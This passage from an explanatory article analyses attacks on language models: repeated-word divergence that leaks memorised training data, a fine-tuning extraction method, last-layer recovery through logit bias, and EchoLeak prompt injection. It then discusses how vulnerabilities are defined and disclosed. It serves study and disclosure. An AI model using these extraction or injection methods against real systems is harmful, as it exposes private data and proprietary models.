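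They also suspected that a long repetition causes divergence by having a similar effect to a special token that OpenAI prevents users from typing. During training, developers join many documents into one long text with this token between them, and the model learns to ignore what came before the token and start afresh. The researchers tested the idea on LLaMA 7B, a Meta model with public weights. As a word repeated, part of the model's internal state came to resemble its state at the very start of a text. This was suggestive, but LLaMA 7B had not leaked training data when it diverged, and the result did not explain how repetition produces the resemblance.

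### Why repetition makes a model diverge

*Interpreting the Repeated Token Phenomenon in Large Language Models* (Yona, Shumailov and colleagues, 2025) gives a more detailed explanation, based on several models with public weights, chiefly Meta's Llama 2. The explanation involves attention, the part of a language model that moves information between tokens.

A model processes text in layers, and for each token it keeps a long list of numbers called a hidden state, which every layer updates. An attention layer updates each token's hidden state with information from that token and the ones before it. It gives each of these tokens a weight, and the weights must add up to one even when no earlier token is relevant, which is often the case. Models learn to put much of the surplus weight on the first token, which contributes little to the result. Researchers call a token that collects attention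 in this way an attention sink.

Attention sinks seem to be a by-product of how developers train language models. *Do New Attention Mechanisms Actually Fix Attention Sinks at Million-Token Context?* (2026) compares two versions of a small model. One learned to predict the next token at every position, as language models do, and placed 31.6% of its attention on the first token. The other learned only to give the answer to a question at the end, and placed 4.9% there. The direction of the effect was the same in all three training runs of each version, but the exact sizes are unreliable because there were so few runs and the first version's results ranged from 9% to 46%.

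To create a sink, a model has to recognise which token comes first. Yona and colleagues found that Llama 2 does this in two stages:

1. In the first attention layer, each token mostly looks for tokens other than itself. The model can only look backwards, so the first token has nothing else to find and attends to itself. This leaves a recognisable mark on its hidden state.
2. Soon afterwards, one or two particular neurons respond to the mark and add very large values to that token's hidden state. Later layers then give the token a great deal of attention.

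When the researchers switched off these "sink neurons", the large values mostly disappeared. This shows that the neurons cause the large values and aren't just correlated with them.

The weak point is the first stage. The layer doesn't check whether a token is in first place. It detects tokens that have found nothing different from themselves, and in a long repetition a token finds almost nothing but copies of itself. Suppose that a prompt has *k* ordinary tokens followed by *n* copies of one token. Let *v* be the information that each copy contributes, *v*₁ to *v*ₖ the information from the ordinary tokens, and *a*₁ to *a*ₖ the weights on them. The attention layer then computes:

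```
for the last copy:      a₁v₁ + … + aₖvₖ + (1 − a₁ − … − aₖ)v
for one token alone:    v
difference:             a₁(v₁ − v) + … + aₖ(vₖ − v)
```

As the copies multiply, the ordinary tokens get less of the total weight. Each weight *a* is at most a constant divided by *n*, so the difference shrinks towards zero. If every token received equal weight, ten tokens of instructions would get 9% of the attention after 100 copies and 1% after 990. A token's position affects only the weights, and the average of identical values is the same whatever the weights are. Yona and colleagues prove that the result also holds for a model with many layers.

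The model therefore treats the last copies like the start of a text. The sink neurons respond to them as they would to a real first token, and the later layers attend heavily to a whole run of sinks instead of the usual one. According to the study, this disrupts the model's normal processing. In the four models examined, the effect required from 450 repetitions for the first LLaMA to 4,000 for a version of Llama 3. In Llama 2, some words never became sinks however often they were repeated, and the study does not establish why.

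The same reasoning may explain why the attack on ChatGPT failed with longer words. A repeated two-token word alternates between two different values, and their average matches neither. Evidence from newer models also fits this reasoning. *Attention Needs to Focus* (2026) reports that repeating one token in Qwen3-4B and BLOOM made the internal measurements almost the same at every position, so that each position resembled a sink. *It's Not RoPE that Creates Sinks* (2026) reports that when the input was a single repeated token, attention didn't concentrate on the first position in any of five models. Inserting one different token made attention concentrate there strongly in both Llama models and in Qwen2-7B, but hardly at all in Pythia 1B.

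All of this evidence comes from models that outsiders can inspect. ChatGPT probably diverged for the same reason, because its behaviour was so similar, but only OpenAI could confirm this.

### The cluster attack and the targeted correction

If this account is right, an attacker shouldn't need to repeat a word, because any text that gives the first layer no clear contrast should work. Yona and colleagues tested this on Llama 2, where an attention layer consists of many units called heads that work in parallel. They found that for many tokens a single head is enough to produce the mark of a first token, and that different heads do this for different clusters of tokens. The head responsible for a cluster can distinguish poorly between the tokens in it. In two of their examples, each made of two different tokens from the same cluster, the second token's hidden state became almost as large as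 the first's (16.5 against 18.4, and 14.3 against 19.0). Other tokens had far smaller values.

They called this the cluster attack. It is a variant of the word-repetition attack because it exploits the same error in identifying which token comes first, but a filter that looks for repeated words would not catch it. The researchers showed that the attack creates false sinks, but did not measure how often it makes a model leak training data. They also found that the first layer's behaviour was specific to Llama 2. The weakness is therefore not limited to repeated words, but nobody has shown that a cluster attack would have extracted anything from ChatGPT.

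The team then wrote a correction that acts directly on the sink neurons. While the model reads a prompt, the correction records a sink neuron's value at the second token, where it is normally small. It then sets the neuron to that value at every later token, including those the model generates. The real first token keeps its sink, so the rest of the model can work as usual. The method assumes that the second token is not itself a false sink.

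Yona and colleagues checked for side effects with five standard tests on three models. Llama 2's scores rose or fell by less than one point. The first LLaMA lost 1.83 points on one test and changed little on the others. Mistral's scores fell on all five tests, by 0.48 to 1.11 points. The researchers call these changes negligible, which seems fair for Llama 2 but a little generous for Mistral.

They give less evidence that the correction works. They show examples in which a corrected model no longer diverges on repeated words, but they don't report how often it diverged before and after. They acknowledge that the correction doesn't fully remove the problem, because a model that can only attend to earlier tokens will always have difficulty with long repetitions. Still, the correction acts on the cause of the divergence instead of the wording of the prompt, so it should stop variants of the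 attack nobody has thought of yet, provided they rely on the same neurons.

Neither the explanation nor the correction addresses memorisation. The researchers say they don't know how false sinks lead the model to release training data. Their main example of a leak, from the open model Pythia 12B, is a paragraph about 3D printing that resembles a passage on a website in the training data. It is a paraphrase, so it would fail the 50-token test. A model might well write something similar about such a common subject without having memorised the page.

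### A second way to the memorised text

If memorisation is a vulnerability in its own right, an attacker should be able to exploit it without making the model diverge. The 2025 paper by Nasr and colleagues describes such an attack, which uses OpenAI's fine-tuning service. This service lets customers train a model further on their own examples, and companies typically use it to teach a model their house style or a specialised task. The researchers used it to undo the chat training. They took 1,000 texts and trained the model to produce each one when given its first few words. The model then behaved like a base model again and continued whatever text it received.

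The researchers prepared two sets of fine-tuning texts, one of ordinary documents from a public collection and the other of passages that the word-repetition attack had extracted. They gave each fine-tuned model 1,000 short prompts from Wikipedia and applied the 50-token test. They excluded any text that appeared in the fine-tuning sets, since the model could have learned it during fine-tuning.

| Model | Before fine-tuning | After training on ordinary documents | After training on extracted passages |
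|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-3.5 | 0.08% | 4.27% | 16.87% |
| GPT-4 | 0.60% | 4.80% | 11.35% |
| LLaMA2-Chat (70B) | 0.0% | 0.12% | 1.44% |

*Share of output tokens in memorised passages*

Fine-tuning on the extracted passages gave the highest rates, but those runs depended on the word-repetition attack having already succeeded. The runs with ordinary documents test the diagnosis better, because an attacker could carry them out without knowing about word repetition. For GPT-3.5, fine-tuning on ordinary documents raised the rate about fiftyfold. Fine-tuning cost $3 for GPT-3.5 and $30 for GPT-4, although only selected researchers could fine-tune GPT-4 at the time.

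Meta also published the base model for LLaMA2-Chat, so the researchers could compare the two. The base model's rate was 4.11%. Alignment training had reduced this to zero in the test, and the best fine-tuning run restored it to only about a third of the base model's rate. A fine-tuned model's rate may therefore be well below what a better attack could reach.

Fine-tuning also let the researchers ask for particular texts, which they couldn't do with word repetition. They gave the model the beginning of a document and checked whether it produced the exact next 50 tokens. It did so for over 75% of known memorised passages that the researchers had kept out of the fine-tuning. For excerpts from published books, which may or may not have been in the training data, the figure was about 4% for GPT-3.5 and 6% for GPT-4. Fine-tuned GPT-4 also reproduced parts of several *New York Times* articles. The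 fine-tuning attack released much less personal information than word repetition had. Across 1,000 outputs, GPT-3.5 gave four phone numbers or email addresses, and only after training on the extracted passages.

### Results on other models

In 2023, the word-repetition attack worked on ChatGPT but on none of the other commercial models the researchers tried. For the 2025 version, they tested separately whether a model diverged and whether it then produced memorised text. All 12 open models they tested diverged, but at very different rates. Pythia 1.4B did so in 85% of runs and the similarly sized OPT 1.3B in 32%, so size alone can't explain the difference. These models hardly ever produced memorised text when they diverged. Pythia 1.4B did so in less than 0.05% of cases and LLaMA 65B in less than 0.14%.

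These open models had memorised a lot of text. With ordinary prompts, 0.45% of Pythia 1.4B's output and 0.79% of LLaMA 65B's came from memorised passages. The word-repetition attack did not work on GPT-4, but fine-tuning showed that it had also memorised a good deal. So a model can diverge without leaking, and it can hold memorised text that this kind of divergence doesn't release. This is good evidence that the researchers were right to count two vulnerabilities.

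Google released its Gemini models after the attack had become public, and the team tried word repetition on Gemini 1.5 Pro. The model diverged in 44% of 3,750 runs. Of the tokens it produced in those runs, 0.35% belonged to memorised passages from 23 documents. The runs cost $113, and the leak was far smaller than ChatGPT's.

The original attack on ChatGPT had stopped working by the time the 2025 version of the paper appeared. Nasr and colleagues write that it "has been patched" but that the general problem of divergence remains. They expect the fine-tuning attack to be harder to stop without significant changes to the fine-tuning service.

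## Deciding what counts as the vulnerability and where it lies

Nasr and colleagues counted two vulnerabilities behind the word-repetition attack, memorisation and divergence. Someone else could count one, or none, from the same evidence. The researchers could only confirm a leak by finding the same text elsewhere, usually on the public web, so a developer might argue that the model had revealed nothing secret. The disagreement is partly about what a vulnerability is. The definition matters because companies use it to decide which reports to accept, and engineers need it to know when a repair is finished.

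### Three definitions, tested on memorisation

The CVE Program's *CVE Numbering Authority (CNA) Operational Rules* (2026), which bind the organisations that assign CVE numbers, define a vulnerability as a weakness in a product that someone can exploit, with harm to confidentiality, integrity or availability. After a semicolon, the definition adds wording much like CERT/CC's about violations of a written or unwritten security policy. It isn't obvious whether a weakness has to meet both halves. Earlier wordings were narrower. The CVE Program's 2021 glossary had only the first half. The CVE definition in *Vulnerabilities*, a page of the US National Vulnerability Database (NVD), places the weakness in "computational logic (e.g., code)" and describes most repairs as involving changes to code.

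Memorisation fits the NVD wording badly. The weights determine what the model computes, but no programmer wrote a stranger's phone number into them, and no programmer can remove it by deleting a line of code. The current rules fit better. A model harms confidentiality when it repeats a phone number from a page its owner has since taken down. Reciting a public poem doesn't harm confidentiality, but it arguably breaks an unwritten policy, because OpenAI keeps its training data secret. Training that stores public text would also store private text in the same way if a developer included any.

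The rules also normally give two weaknesses separate CVE numbers if developers can fix each one independently. A recent example is a pair of weaknesses in Ollama, a program for running language models on one's own computer. According to the security news site The Hacker News, Ollama's Windows updater didn't check the signature on an update, and it also let the update server influence where on the disk the installer went. The missing check alone lets an attacker who controls the update server run code until the next genuine update overwrites it. With both weaknesses, the attacker's code survives and runs at every login. Developers could fix either weakness without fixing the other, and each has its own CVE number.

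Memorisation and divergence look like a similar pair. Yona and colleagues' correction acts on divergence and leaves the memorised text in place, while retraining without the sensitive passages would remove that text but not the divergence. But two other CVE rules may mean that divergence isn't a separate vulnerability. Under the first, behaviour with no effect on security shouldn't count, and the open models that Nasr and colleagues tested diverged while leaking almost nothing. Under the second, the ability to get around an "inherently imperfect" protection usually shouldn't count either. If alignment training is only an imperfect protection against leaking memorised text, then divergence is a way around it, and memorisation is the only vulnerability. The rules make an exception when the protection itself has a specific vulnerability, and the error in how models recognise the first token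 might qualify.

The CVE rules could therefore support a count of one or two, but they give little support to a count of none.

*Coordinated Flaw Disclosure for AI* (Cattell, Ghosh and Kaffee, 2024) argues that definitions from software security leave out too much, especially bias. It proposes the term "flaw" for any unexpected model behaviour outside the stated intent and scope of the model's design. The developer states both in a model card, a document describing the model's purpose and known limits. Reciting training data would probably be a flaw in a chat model presented as a safe assistant, but might not be one in a base model released for others to build on.

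Much therefore depends on what the developer writes. Cattell and colleagues intend the scope statement mainly to exclude known problems that the developer can't or won't resolve within a year. A developer could therefore list memorisation as a known limitation and reject reports about it while the model went on leaking phone numbers. As partial protection against this, they propose an independent panel to hear appeals. For common uses that the card doesn't cover, the panel could recommend publishing a harmful problem anyway.

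Under one classification, the ChatGPT attack is a systematic error, which comes from the training data and which a developer can correct by changing that data. This describes memorisation fairly well but leaves out divergence, which seems to come from how models process repetition and not from any particular text they learned.

*FLARE-AI* (Longpre, Zhu and colleagues, 2026), a proposal for a shared reporting system, defines a flaw by the explicit or implicit policy it breaches, not by the model's intended design. Because implicit policies count, a privacy problem can still be a flaw if the developer leaves privacy out of the model card. Memorisation easily qualifies, though people can still dispute what the implicit policy was.

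The third approach is to look only at the outcome. Piao, Li and Woods (2025), in *"Abuse Risks are Often Inherent to Product Features"*, contrast it with the view that AI vulnerabilities are special because they exploit learned rules. On the outcome view, a command that leaks sensitive data reveals a vulnerability whether it works through a database or a language model. Vendors' policies tend to follow this approach. Piao and colleagues examined 264 AI vendors, of which only 48 explicitly mentioned AI vulnerabilities. Vulnerabilities defined by a security goal were in scope 91% of the time, compared with 71% for prompt injection (hiding instructions in text that a model processes) and 27% for jailbreaking (getting a model to ignore its restrictions).

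The outcome view is the most convenient of the three for someone reporting memorisation. A leaked phone number is enough, and an outsider without access to the weights doesn't have to explain how it got out. But the view is much less help with the repair. Once ChatGPT refuses requests to repeat a word forever, the breach appears to be over, even if the weights still contain the memorised data. A company can sensibly accept reports based on outcomes, as long as its engineers then look for the cause.

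### Whether a learned model can have an exploited state

Cattell and colleagues also raise a more basic objection, that models "lack distinct exploited and non-exploited states". A database either runs a visitor's text as a command or doesn't, whereas a language model answers every prompt with the same kind of computation, and a leak differs from a normal reply only in its content. ChatGPT produced some memorised text even with ordinary prompts, though far less often than under attack.

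Users also expect these systems to make mistakes. In Cattell and colleagues' example of a spam filter, a report that it missed one email is of little use, and even thousands of missed emails may not lead the vendor to change its code. A report becomes valuable when it describes an easy way to get past the filter. When a problem falls between an isolated error and a dependable procedure, someone has to judge whether it happens too often or causes too much harm.

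Memorisation poses a further difficulty because recall is also useful. A person who asks for a famous poem or a standard software licence wants the exact text, and training that removed all verbatim recall would make the model worse at providing it. Patches for machine learning systems in general often fix the vulnerability only partly and cost money or reduce performance, according to *Securing AI*, a report written before ChatGPT by CSET, a technology policy centre at Georgetown University. The report also warned that many of these systems may be inherently vulnerable.

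These objections count against treating memorisation as a simple defect, like a missing line of code. They are weaker against the distinction between a vulnerability and an exploit. That distinction requires only a lasting condition of the model that makes a whole group of attacks more likely to succeed, not two distinct states. It implies that a variant should still work if a repair addresses only the wording of one attack.

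Nasr and colleagues made this prediction about ChatGPT in 2023, and their later fine-tuning attack extracted memorised text from GPT-3.5 without relying on word repetition. The same team made the prediction and tested it, so it would be good for others to repeat the result. Still, the attack would have failed if alignment training had erased the memorised passages.

Because a model's recall of text is useful, the vulnerability is better described as its ability to output particular passages that the developer ought to withhold, such as private contact details. A fix has to stop the model from outputting those passages but can leave its recall of poems intact. People will still disagree about which passages to withhold. For example, an author whose novel the model can recite may well disagree with the developer.

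### Ordinary code: the Ollama memory leak

Once an attack is known, engineers have to find the layer that allows it. They can change one layer at a time and see whether the attack still works. If it works no matter which model the program loads, the fault is probably in the program. If similar models resist the attack behind a different interface, the fault is more likely to be in the interface. Outsiders can rarely run such tests on a commercial system, but they can sometimes compare one company's product with another's.

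Ollama's memory leak, CVE-2026-7482, is a clear case of a fault in ordinary code. Ollama loads a model from a file that lists the size of its data. Versions before 0.17.1 could accept a file in which the listed size was larger than the actual size. While converting such a file to another format, the program read past the end of the data and into other contents of its memory. It wrote the result to a new model file, which an attacker could then make the server send elsewhere.

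The Hacker News reports a severity score of 9.1 and an estimate of more than 300,000 affected servers. The leaked memory could include access keys, the instructions that operators give their models, and other users' conversations. An attacker didn't need an account, because Ollama's interface doesn't require a login by default.

The fault lies in the code and not in anything the language model had learned, although the outcome resembles training-data extraction in that an AI system reveals private text. Retraining the model or teaching it to refuse requests would not have helped. A programmer can find the fault by reading the code, and a check that compares the declared size with the real one stops every file of this kind, including those that nobody has written yet. Operators then have to install the repaired version. The article also recommends firewalls and login requirements, which are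 blocks that limit who can send a file to the server.

### The interface: recovering part of a production model

Carlini, Paleka and colleagues (2024), in *Stealing Part of a Production Language Model*, recovered some of the weights of OpenAI's models through the same programming interface that paying customers used. The weakness they exploited comes from the model's last step, in which it turns its hidden state into a score for every token in its vocabulary. The model multiplies the *h* numbers in the hidden state by a fixed grid of weights, *W*, which has *h* columns and a row for each token:

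```
scores = W × hidden state
```

The vocabulary is much larger than *h*. In the smallest LLaMA model, for example, *h* is 4,096 and there are 32,000 tokens. The scores therefore can't vary freely. Take a toy model with four tokens and *h* = 2, and suppose that the columns of *W* are (1, 0, 2, 1) and (0, 1, 1, 3). A hidden state of (2, 1) gives these scores:

```
2 × (1, 0, 2, 1) + 1 × (0, 1, 1, 3) = (2, 1, 5, 5)
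```

Any other hidden state also gives some mixture of the same two columns. Once an observer has seen two sets of scores that aren't multiples of each other, every later set is a combination of those two. The observer can then work out that *h* is 2 and recover *W*, except for how its columns have been mixed together.

Real scores contain rounding errors, so the researchers measured how much the scores varied in each independent direction and looked for the point where the variation dropped sharply. For Pythia 1.4B, an open model, the drop came almost exactly at the model's true number of dimensions, 2,048. For GPT-2 Small, the method gave 757 instead of 768, and the researchers found that the model effectively uses only that many dimensions.

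The researchers knew of no commercial service that returned a full set of scores. But OpenAI's interface returned probabilities for the five most likely tokens and let customers raise or lower the scores of chosen tokens, a feature called logit bias. Developers use logit bias for legitimate purposes, such as restricting a model to certain kinds of output. The researchers used it to bring other tokens into the top five, then worked out those tokens' original scores from the returned probabilities.

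With OpenAI's permission, Carlini and colleagues recovered the whole last layer of two older models, ada and babbage, for $4 and $12. For two versions of gpt-3.5-turbo they recovered only the hidden dimension, *h*, and estimated that recovering the full layer would cost about $2,000 and $8,000. OpenAI confirmed that their values of *h* were correct and asked them not to publish those for gpt-3.5-turbo. Finlayson, Ren and Swayamdipta independently discovered the same weakness and published an estimate of about 4,096 for gpt-3.5-turbo in *Logits of API-Protected LLMs Leak Proprietary Information* (2024). One layer is far from enough to make a working copy of a model, and Carlini and colleagues saw no immediate practical consequences.

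The interface is a better place to locate the vulnerability than the model's design. The attack does depend on *h* being smaller than the vocabulary, but Finlayson and colleagues note that most modern language models share this property, and not all of them were exposed. The team's blog post, also called *Stealing Part of a Production Language Model* (2024), gives Anthropic as an example of a company that was not vulnerable, because it had never offered logit bias.

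It was also the easier place to make a repair. The researchers suggested adding another stage to the architecture before the final scores, but this would make the model less efficient. Removing logit bias would deprive customers of a useful feature, but replacing it with a list of forbidden tokens would preserve some of its uses and still prevent the attack. Adding random noise to the scores could also prevent the attack, but might make the model less useful.

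Google, and then OpenAI on 3 March 2024, took the milder step of limiting customers' use of logit bias and returned probabilities in the same query. According to the blog post, this makes the attack considerably more expensive but not impossible. Carlini and colleagues had already worked out how to recover scores from logit bias alone. Their best method needed 3.7 queries per score, about 15 times the 0.25 needed with both features. The change is therefore a block, but a much better one than a filter for a particular prompt, because it affects every attack that needs both features in the same query.

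Whether any vulnerability remains depends on how broadly one describes it. *What do your logits know?* (2026) reports that the scores of the most likely tokens also reveal details the query didn't ask about. Predictions of these details from the top 20 scores were better than chance with as few as 100 training examples. This doesn't involve stealing *W*, but the information leaks through the same channel. An engineer who had described the vulnerability as "customers can reconstruct the last layer" would have had no reason to look for this leak.

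### The application and the model: EchoLeak

EchoLeak (CVE-2025-32711) was a vulnerability in Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant that answers employees' questions using their company's emails and documents. Aim Security, a security company, made it public in June 2025. An outsider could send an employee an email containing instructions for the assistant. If the employee later asked a related question, Copilot could retrieve the email along with internal documents, follow the outsider's instructions, and put confidential information into a web address that the employee's software contacted automatically. The employee didn't have to click on anything. Microsoft fixed the vulnerability on its own servers, so customers had nothing to install.

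The attack needed a model that would follow instructions in an email it was only supposed to read. It also needed an application that gave the model confidential documents and a way to send information out. Microsoft could change the application, but repairing one product did not remove the model's tendency to follow such instructions, which is a general weakness of language models.

In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)* (2025), published by the UK's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC), David C argues that language models may always be vulnerable to prompt injection. Prepared statements prevent SQL injection by relying on the database's separation of commands from data. David C writes that many security specialists expect prompt injection to have the same kind of remedy, but a language model has no such separation. It processes a developer's instructions and a stranger's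 email as one sequence of tokens. Developers can mark the email as data or train the model to give it less authority, which makes attacks harder, but the model may still follow instructions in the email.

David C prefers to call a language model an "inherently confusable deputy". In security, a confused deputy is a program tricked into using its permissions for someone who lacks them. Programmers can usually fix an ordinary confused deputy. With a language model, he argues, they should assume that the trick will sometimes work and limit the damage with conventional code. He is particularly wary of filters for known attack phrases, because there are endless ways to reword an attack. He says there is a good chance that nobody will ever fully solve the problem, but his argument rests on how current models work, so a different design could change the answer.

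One recommended rule, which came out of a discussion between Simon Willison and Baibhav Bista, is that a model should have only the permissions of whoever wrote the text it is processing. Under a strict version of this rule, Copilot would lose access to internal documents while it was reading an outsider's email, which would stop the EchoLeak attack however the email was worded. But Copilot also couldn't answer questions that required both the email and the documents, and answering such questions is much of the reason for having such an assistant.

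Under the CVE rules, when several products are vulnerable because they rely on the same component, each gets its own CVE number if that component can be used securely, and they all share one if it can't. EchoLeak got its own number, which suggests that the fault lay in how Copilot used the model. The CVE Board's AI working group expressed a similar view, that most problems arise in the applications of models rather than in the models themselves (CVE Board, 2025). David C's argument is compatible with this for applications that can tolerate a model that is sometimes fooled. For those that can't, he suggests that a language model may be the wrong tool.

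For each case, the table separates the attack from the weakness and shows who is in a position to repair it.

| Case | Exploit | Vulnerability | Layer | Who can repair it |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| ChatGPT word repetition | A request to repeat one word forever | Memorised sensitive text, and divergence that helps release it | Weights | OpenAI |
| Ollama memory leak | A model file that declares a false size | No adequate check of the declared size | Ordinary code | Ollama's developers; each operator must then update |
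| Recovery of a model's last layer | Many queries that combine logit bias with returned probabilities | An interface that reveals enough to reconstruct the layer | Interface | The company that runs the interface |
| EchoLeak, the product | An email with instructions for the assistant | Outsiders' text could direct an assistant that had confidential data and a way to send it out | Application | Microsoft |
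| EchoLeak, the underlying weakness | The same email, or any other text the model reads | No firm boundary between instructions and data | Model | Nobody yet; developers of models and applications can reduce the risk |

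## Reporting a finding to those who can act on it

Whoever controls the layer that contains a vulnerability should usually hear about it first. Microsoft could stop EchoLeak on its own servers, while only OpenAI could change the weights behind the ChatGPT leak. But an outsider often can't tell which layer is at fault, and the company responsible may not accept reports about that kind of weakness.

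### Whom to tell

When a company builds its product on another organisation's model, both organisations may need the report. The company can quickly restrict what the model has access to, and the model's developer can change the weights. Piao and colleagues point out that researchers may not know which model an application uses. They recommend that application companies either forward relevant reports to the model's developer or name the AI services they depend on. Until more companies do this, a reporter can ask the application company to pass the report on.

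Flaws often transfer between similar systems, yet researchers may tell only one developer, Longpre and Appel write in *General-Purpose AI Needs Coordinated Flaw Reporting*. That developer probably won't tell others whose systems have the same flaw. In their work on FLARE-AI, Longpre and colleagues found little evidence that AI developers share reports with competitors.

A developer whose current model resists an attack may still need to know about it, because its next model may not. Word repetition worked on only one of the commercial models tested in 2023, but it later made Google's Gemini 1.5 Pro leak a little training data. But every extra recipient makes an embargo harder to keep. One compromise is to send the working prompt only to developers whose models it affects, and a general description of the weakness to the others.

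A coordinator such as CERT/CC is most useful when many developers share a weakness or when the first developer contacted doesn't respond. *AI Jailbreak Disclosure Is Broken. Here's How to Fix It* (Barton-Cooper and Gleave, 2026) describes a report that received only an automated reply. In October 2025 Barton-Cooper emailed xAI, now SpaceXAI, about a universal jailbreak, meaning one that works across a wide range of harmful requests. He included redacted evidence that the model had given step-by-step instructions for a chemical weapon. *Policy Pulse* (2026), a newsletter on disclosure policy, argues that universal jailbreaks are "coordination problems, not single-vendor bugs", which would be a reason to involve a coordinator from the start.

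### What vendors accept

Piao and colleagues studied 264 AI vendors from product lists by Gartner, a market research company, including the largest AI developers. They found that 96 (36%) had no public way to report a vulnerability, probably, they think, because many AI vendors are young companies that put growth ahead of security. Another 21 gave only an email address or similar contact. About 16% accepted reports without paying for them, and 40% ran bug bounties, which reward people for valid reports.

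Forty-eight vendors, 18% of the total, had policies that mentioned AI vulnerabilities. About half of model providers mentioned them. Only 8% of model providers had no reporting channel, compared with 68% of companies that sell data science platforms.

The policies that mention a type of vulnerability either accept or exclude it:

| Type of vulnerability | Accept | Exclude | Share that accept |
|---|---|---|---|
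| Model extraction (copying a model or its weights) | 9 | 1 | 90% |
| Prompt injection | 10 | 4 | 71% |
| Data leakage | 4 | 2 | 67% |
| Jailbreaking | 3 | 8 | 27% |
| Hallucination (false statements by the model) | 1 | 6 | 14% |

The percentages are easy to misread because each is calculated from a different, very small number of policies. The 90% for model extraction means nine of the ten policies that mention it, and those nine represent about 3% of all the vendors in the study. Vendors may still fix AI vulnerabilities that their policies don't mention. Cursor, which makes a programming tool, fixed one that let attackers run code through prompt injection, although its policy doesn't mention AI vulnerabilities.

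Training-data extraction has no category of its own. It could count as data leakage or as an inference attack, in which someone works out facts about the training data from a model's replies. Four of the five policies that mention inference attacks accept reports of them. Vendors most readily accept vulnerabilities that breach a familiar security goal, so a report has a better chance of being accepted if it opens with the outcome, such as "strangers can obtain people's phone numbers", and then explains the technique.

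Vendors give several reasons for excluding AI findings. Piao and colleagues counted eight vendors that required more evidence of harm, seven that regarded the behaviour as expected, and five that said it couldn't be reproduced reliably. Four considered the risk low, and two, including OpenAI, argued that they could not patch such problems directly.

Google's *Celebrating One Year of AI Bug Bounties at Alphabet* explains why the company left jailbreaks out of its programme. A jailbreak typically affects only the session of the person who uses it, so its effect on other users is hard to assess. It is also hard to decide whether two jailbreaks are the same, which matters when only the first reporter gets paid.

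The point about sessions doesn't apply well to training-data extraction, because the attacker sees the leak in their own session but the leaked phone number belongs to somebody else. Duplicates are still hard to recognise, though. If 50 people each report a different repeated word, a company that pays for every exploit will pay 50 times for the same weakness. It could avoid this by paying once per vulnerability, but then someone has to trace the cause before the company can settle the claim.

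The lack of a direct fix is a better reason to refuse payment for a report than to refuse the report itself, because a developer who can't remove a weakness can still block the known attack and look for variants.

Whether a report is excluded can depend on the example the reporter chooses. Under Google's (2023) criteria for AI reports, output that appeared to be copyrighted was out of scope and had its own reporting channel. The word-repetition attack produced personal contact details as well as parts of novels. Under those criteria, a report of the attack that opened with a page from a novel could have gone to the wrong team.

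### What the main programmes pay for

The three largest American model developers all pay for some reports, but for quite different things.

OpenAI (2026) opened a public Safety Bug Bounty on 25 March, alongside its existing programme for security vulnerabilities. It covers attacks in which outside text takes control of an AI agent, leaks of OpenAI's proprietary information, and ways to evade account restrictions. Attacks on agents must work at least half the time to qualify. OpenAI's safety and security teams can transfer reports between the two programmes. According to Briefly's *OpenAI Launches Bug Bounty Program for Abuse and Safety Risks*, the highest reward is $7,500, for reports of severe, consistently reproducible problems with clear suggestions for dealing with them. Jailbreaks are out of scope, except in occasional private programmes on subjects such as biological risk.

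Anthropic's *Model Safety Bug Bounty Program* (2026) offers up to $35,000 for a new universal jailbreak that gets past its safety filters and extracts detailed answers to a set of harmful biological questions. Applicants must sign a non-disclosure agreement before they see the questions. Anthropic takes reports of conventional security flaws separately. A newer, unpaid programme covers jailbreaks that get help with cyberattacks from its model Claude Fable 5. Barton-Cooper and Gleave report that anyone can use it without a non-disclosure agreement.

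Google pays for reports of security attacks on its AI products, such as an email that makes an assistant unlock the recipient's front door. Particle News' *Google launches dedicated AI bug bounty with rewards up to $30,000* puts the maximum reward at $20,000, or $30,000 with bonuses for quality and novelty. The maximum is $15,000 for attacks that steal sensitive data and $5,000 for attacks that steal a model. In NDTV's *Google Is Offering Up To Rs 26 Lakh For Finding Bugs*, two Google managers say that a reward programme isn't "the right format" for problems with content.

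| Programme | Main scope | Highest payment | Important condition |
|---|---|---|---|
| OpenAI Safety Bug Bounty | Hijacked agents, proprietary information, account restrictions | $7,500 | Excludes jailbreaks |
| Anthropic model safety | Universal jailbreaks on biological threats | $35,000 | Application and non-disclosure agreement |
| Anthropic cyber jailbreaks | Help with cyberattacks from Claude Fable 5 | None | Reporter agrees the timing of publication with Anthropic |
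| Google AI programme | Security attacks through AI products | $30,000 with bonuses | Excludes jailbreaks and content problems |

If someone discovered an attack like word repetition on ChatGPT today, it would not be on OpenAI's list. Text that a model has memorised from the web isn't obviously OpenAI's proprietary information, and the attack doesn't take over an agent. The reporter's best hope would be a clause that allows rewards for other flaws if they lead directly to user harm and have "actionable, discrete remediation steps". A filter for repeated words would meet the remediation condition more easily than retraining the model without sensitive passages. The clause may therefore favour reports that propose a block, even when the reporter knows a block won't be enough.

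Some programmes also restrict whom else a reporter may tell. Anthropic's model safety programme forbids participants from revealing jailbreaks outside it without permission, even after Anthropic has dealt with them. According to Barton-Cooper and Gleave, OpenAI's private programme has a similar rule. They consider it unclear whether participants may warn another developer whose model has the same weakness. Anthropic's cyber programme explicitly allows this. A reporter who suspects that several models are affected should read these terms before submitting.

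Barton-Cooper and Gleave also object that developers judge severity by private standards and have a reason to understate it. Gleave runs FAR.AI, a non-profit that tests models for many of these developers, so they both know the process well but have a stake in changing it. Anthropic's terms support part of the complaint, since they describe an internal grading rubric and leave the decision to the company's discretion. Anthropic has since published a severity scale for cyber jailbreaks, developed with Amazon, Microsoft, Google and others. Barton-Cooper and Gleave want similar scales for other kinds of harm, and an independent expert to hear appeals.

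Running such a programme well takes preparation. The NCSC and the UK government's AI Security Institute (AISI) have published principles for programmes that collect safeguard bypasses, their term for ways around a model's protections. Professional Security reports that the principles cover both programmes that pay for reports and programmes that accept them without paying. The two bodies started from the NCSC's guidance for ordinary software and drew on AISI's experience judging a public competition to attack AI agents.

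Infosecurity Magazine's *UK NCSC Supports Public Disclosure for AI Safeguard Bypass Threats* sets out the main principles:

- The developer should define the scope clearly, so that participants know what counts as success.
- It should review its own safeguards and deal with the weaknesses it finds before inviting outsiders.
- Reports should be easy to track and reproduce, for example with unique identifiers and tools for copying and sharing an attack.

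The NCSC and AISI also warn that sorting reports can take a lot of work and that having a programme doesn't by itself make a model safer. They leave open how to judge severity when nobody knows where a model will be used, and how developers should cooperate on attacks that transfer between models.

### Legal protection for researchers

Testing a system without permission can breach its terms of service. Longpre and Appel note that these terms may prohibit "reverse engineering" or "automatic data collection", and an extraction study needs thousands of automated queries. They want companies to offer a safe harbour, a promise not to take legal action against researchers unless there is evidence that they broke the company's rules for testing.

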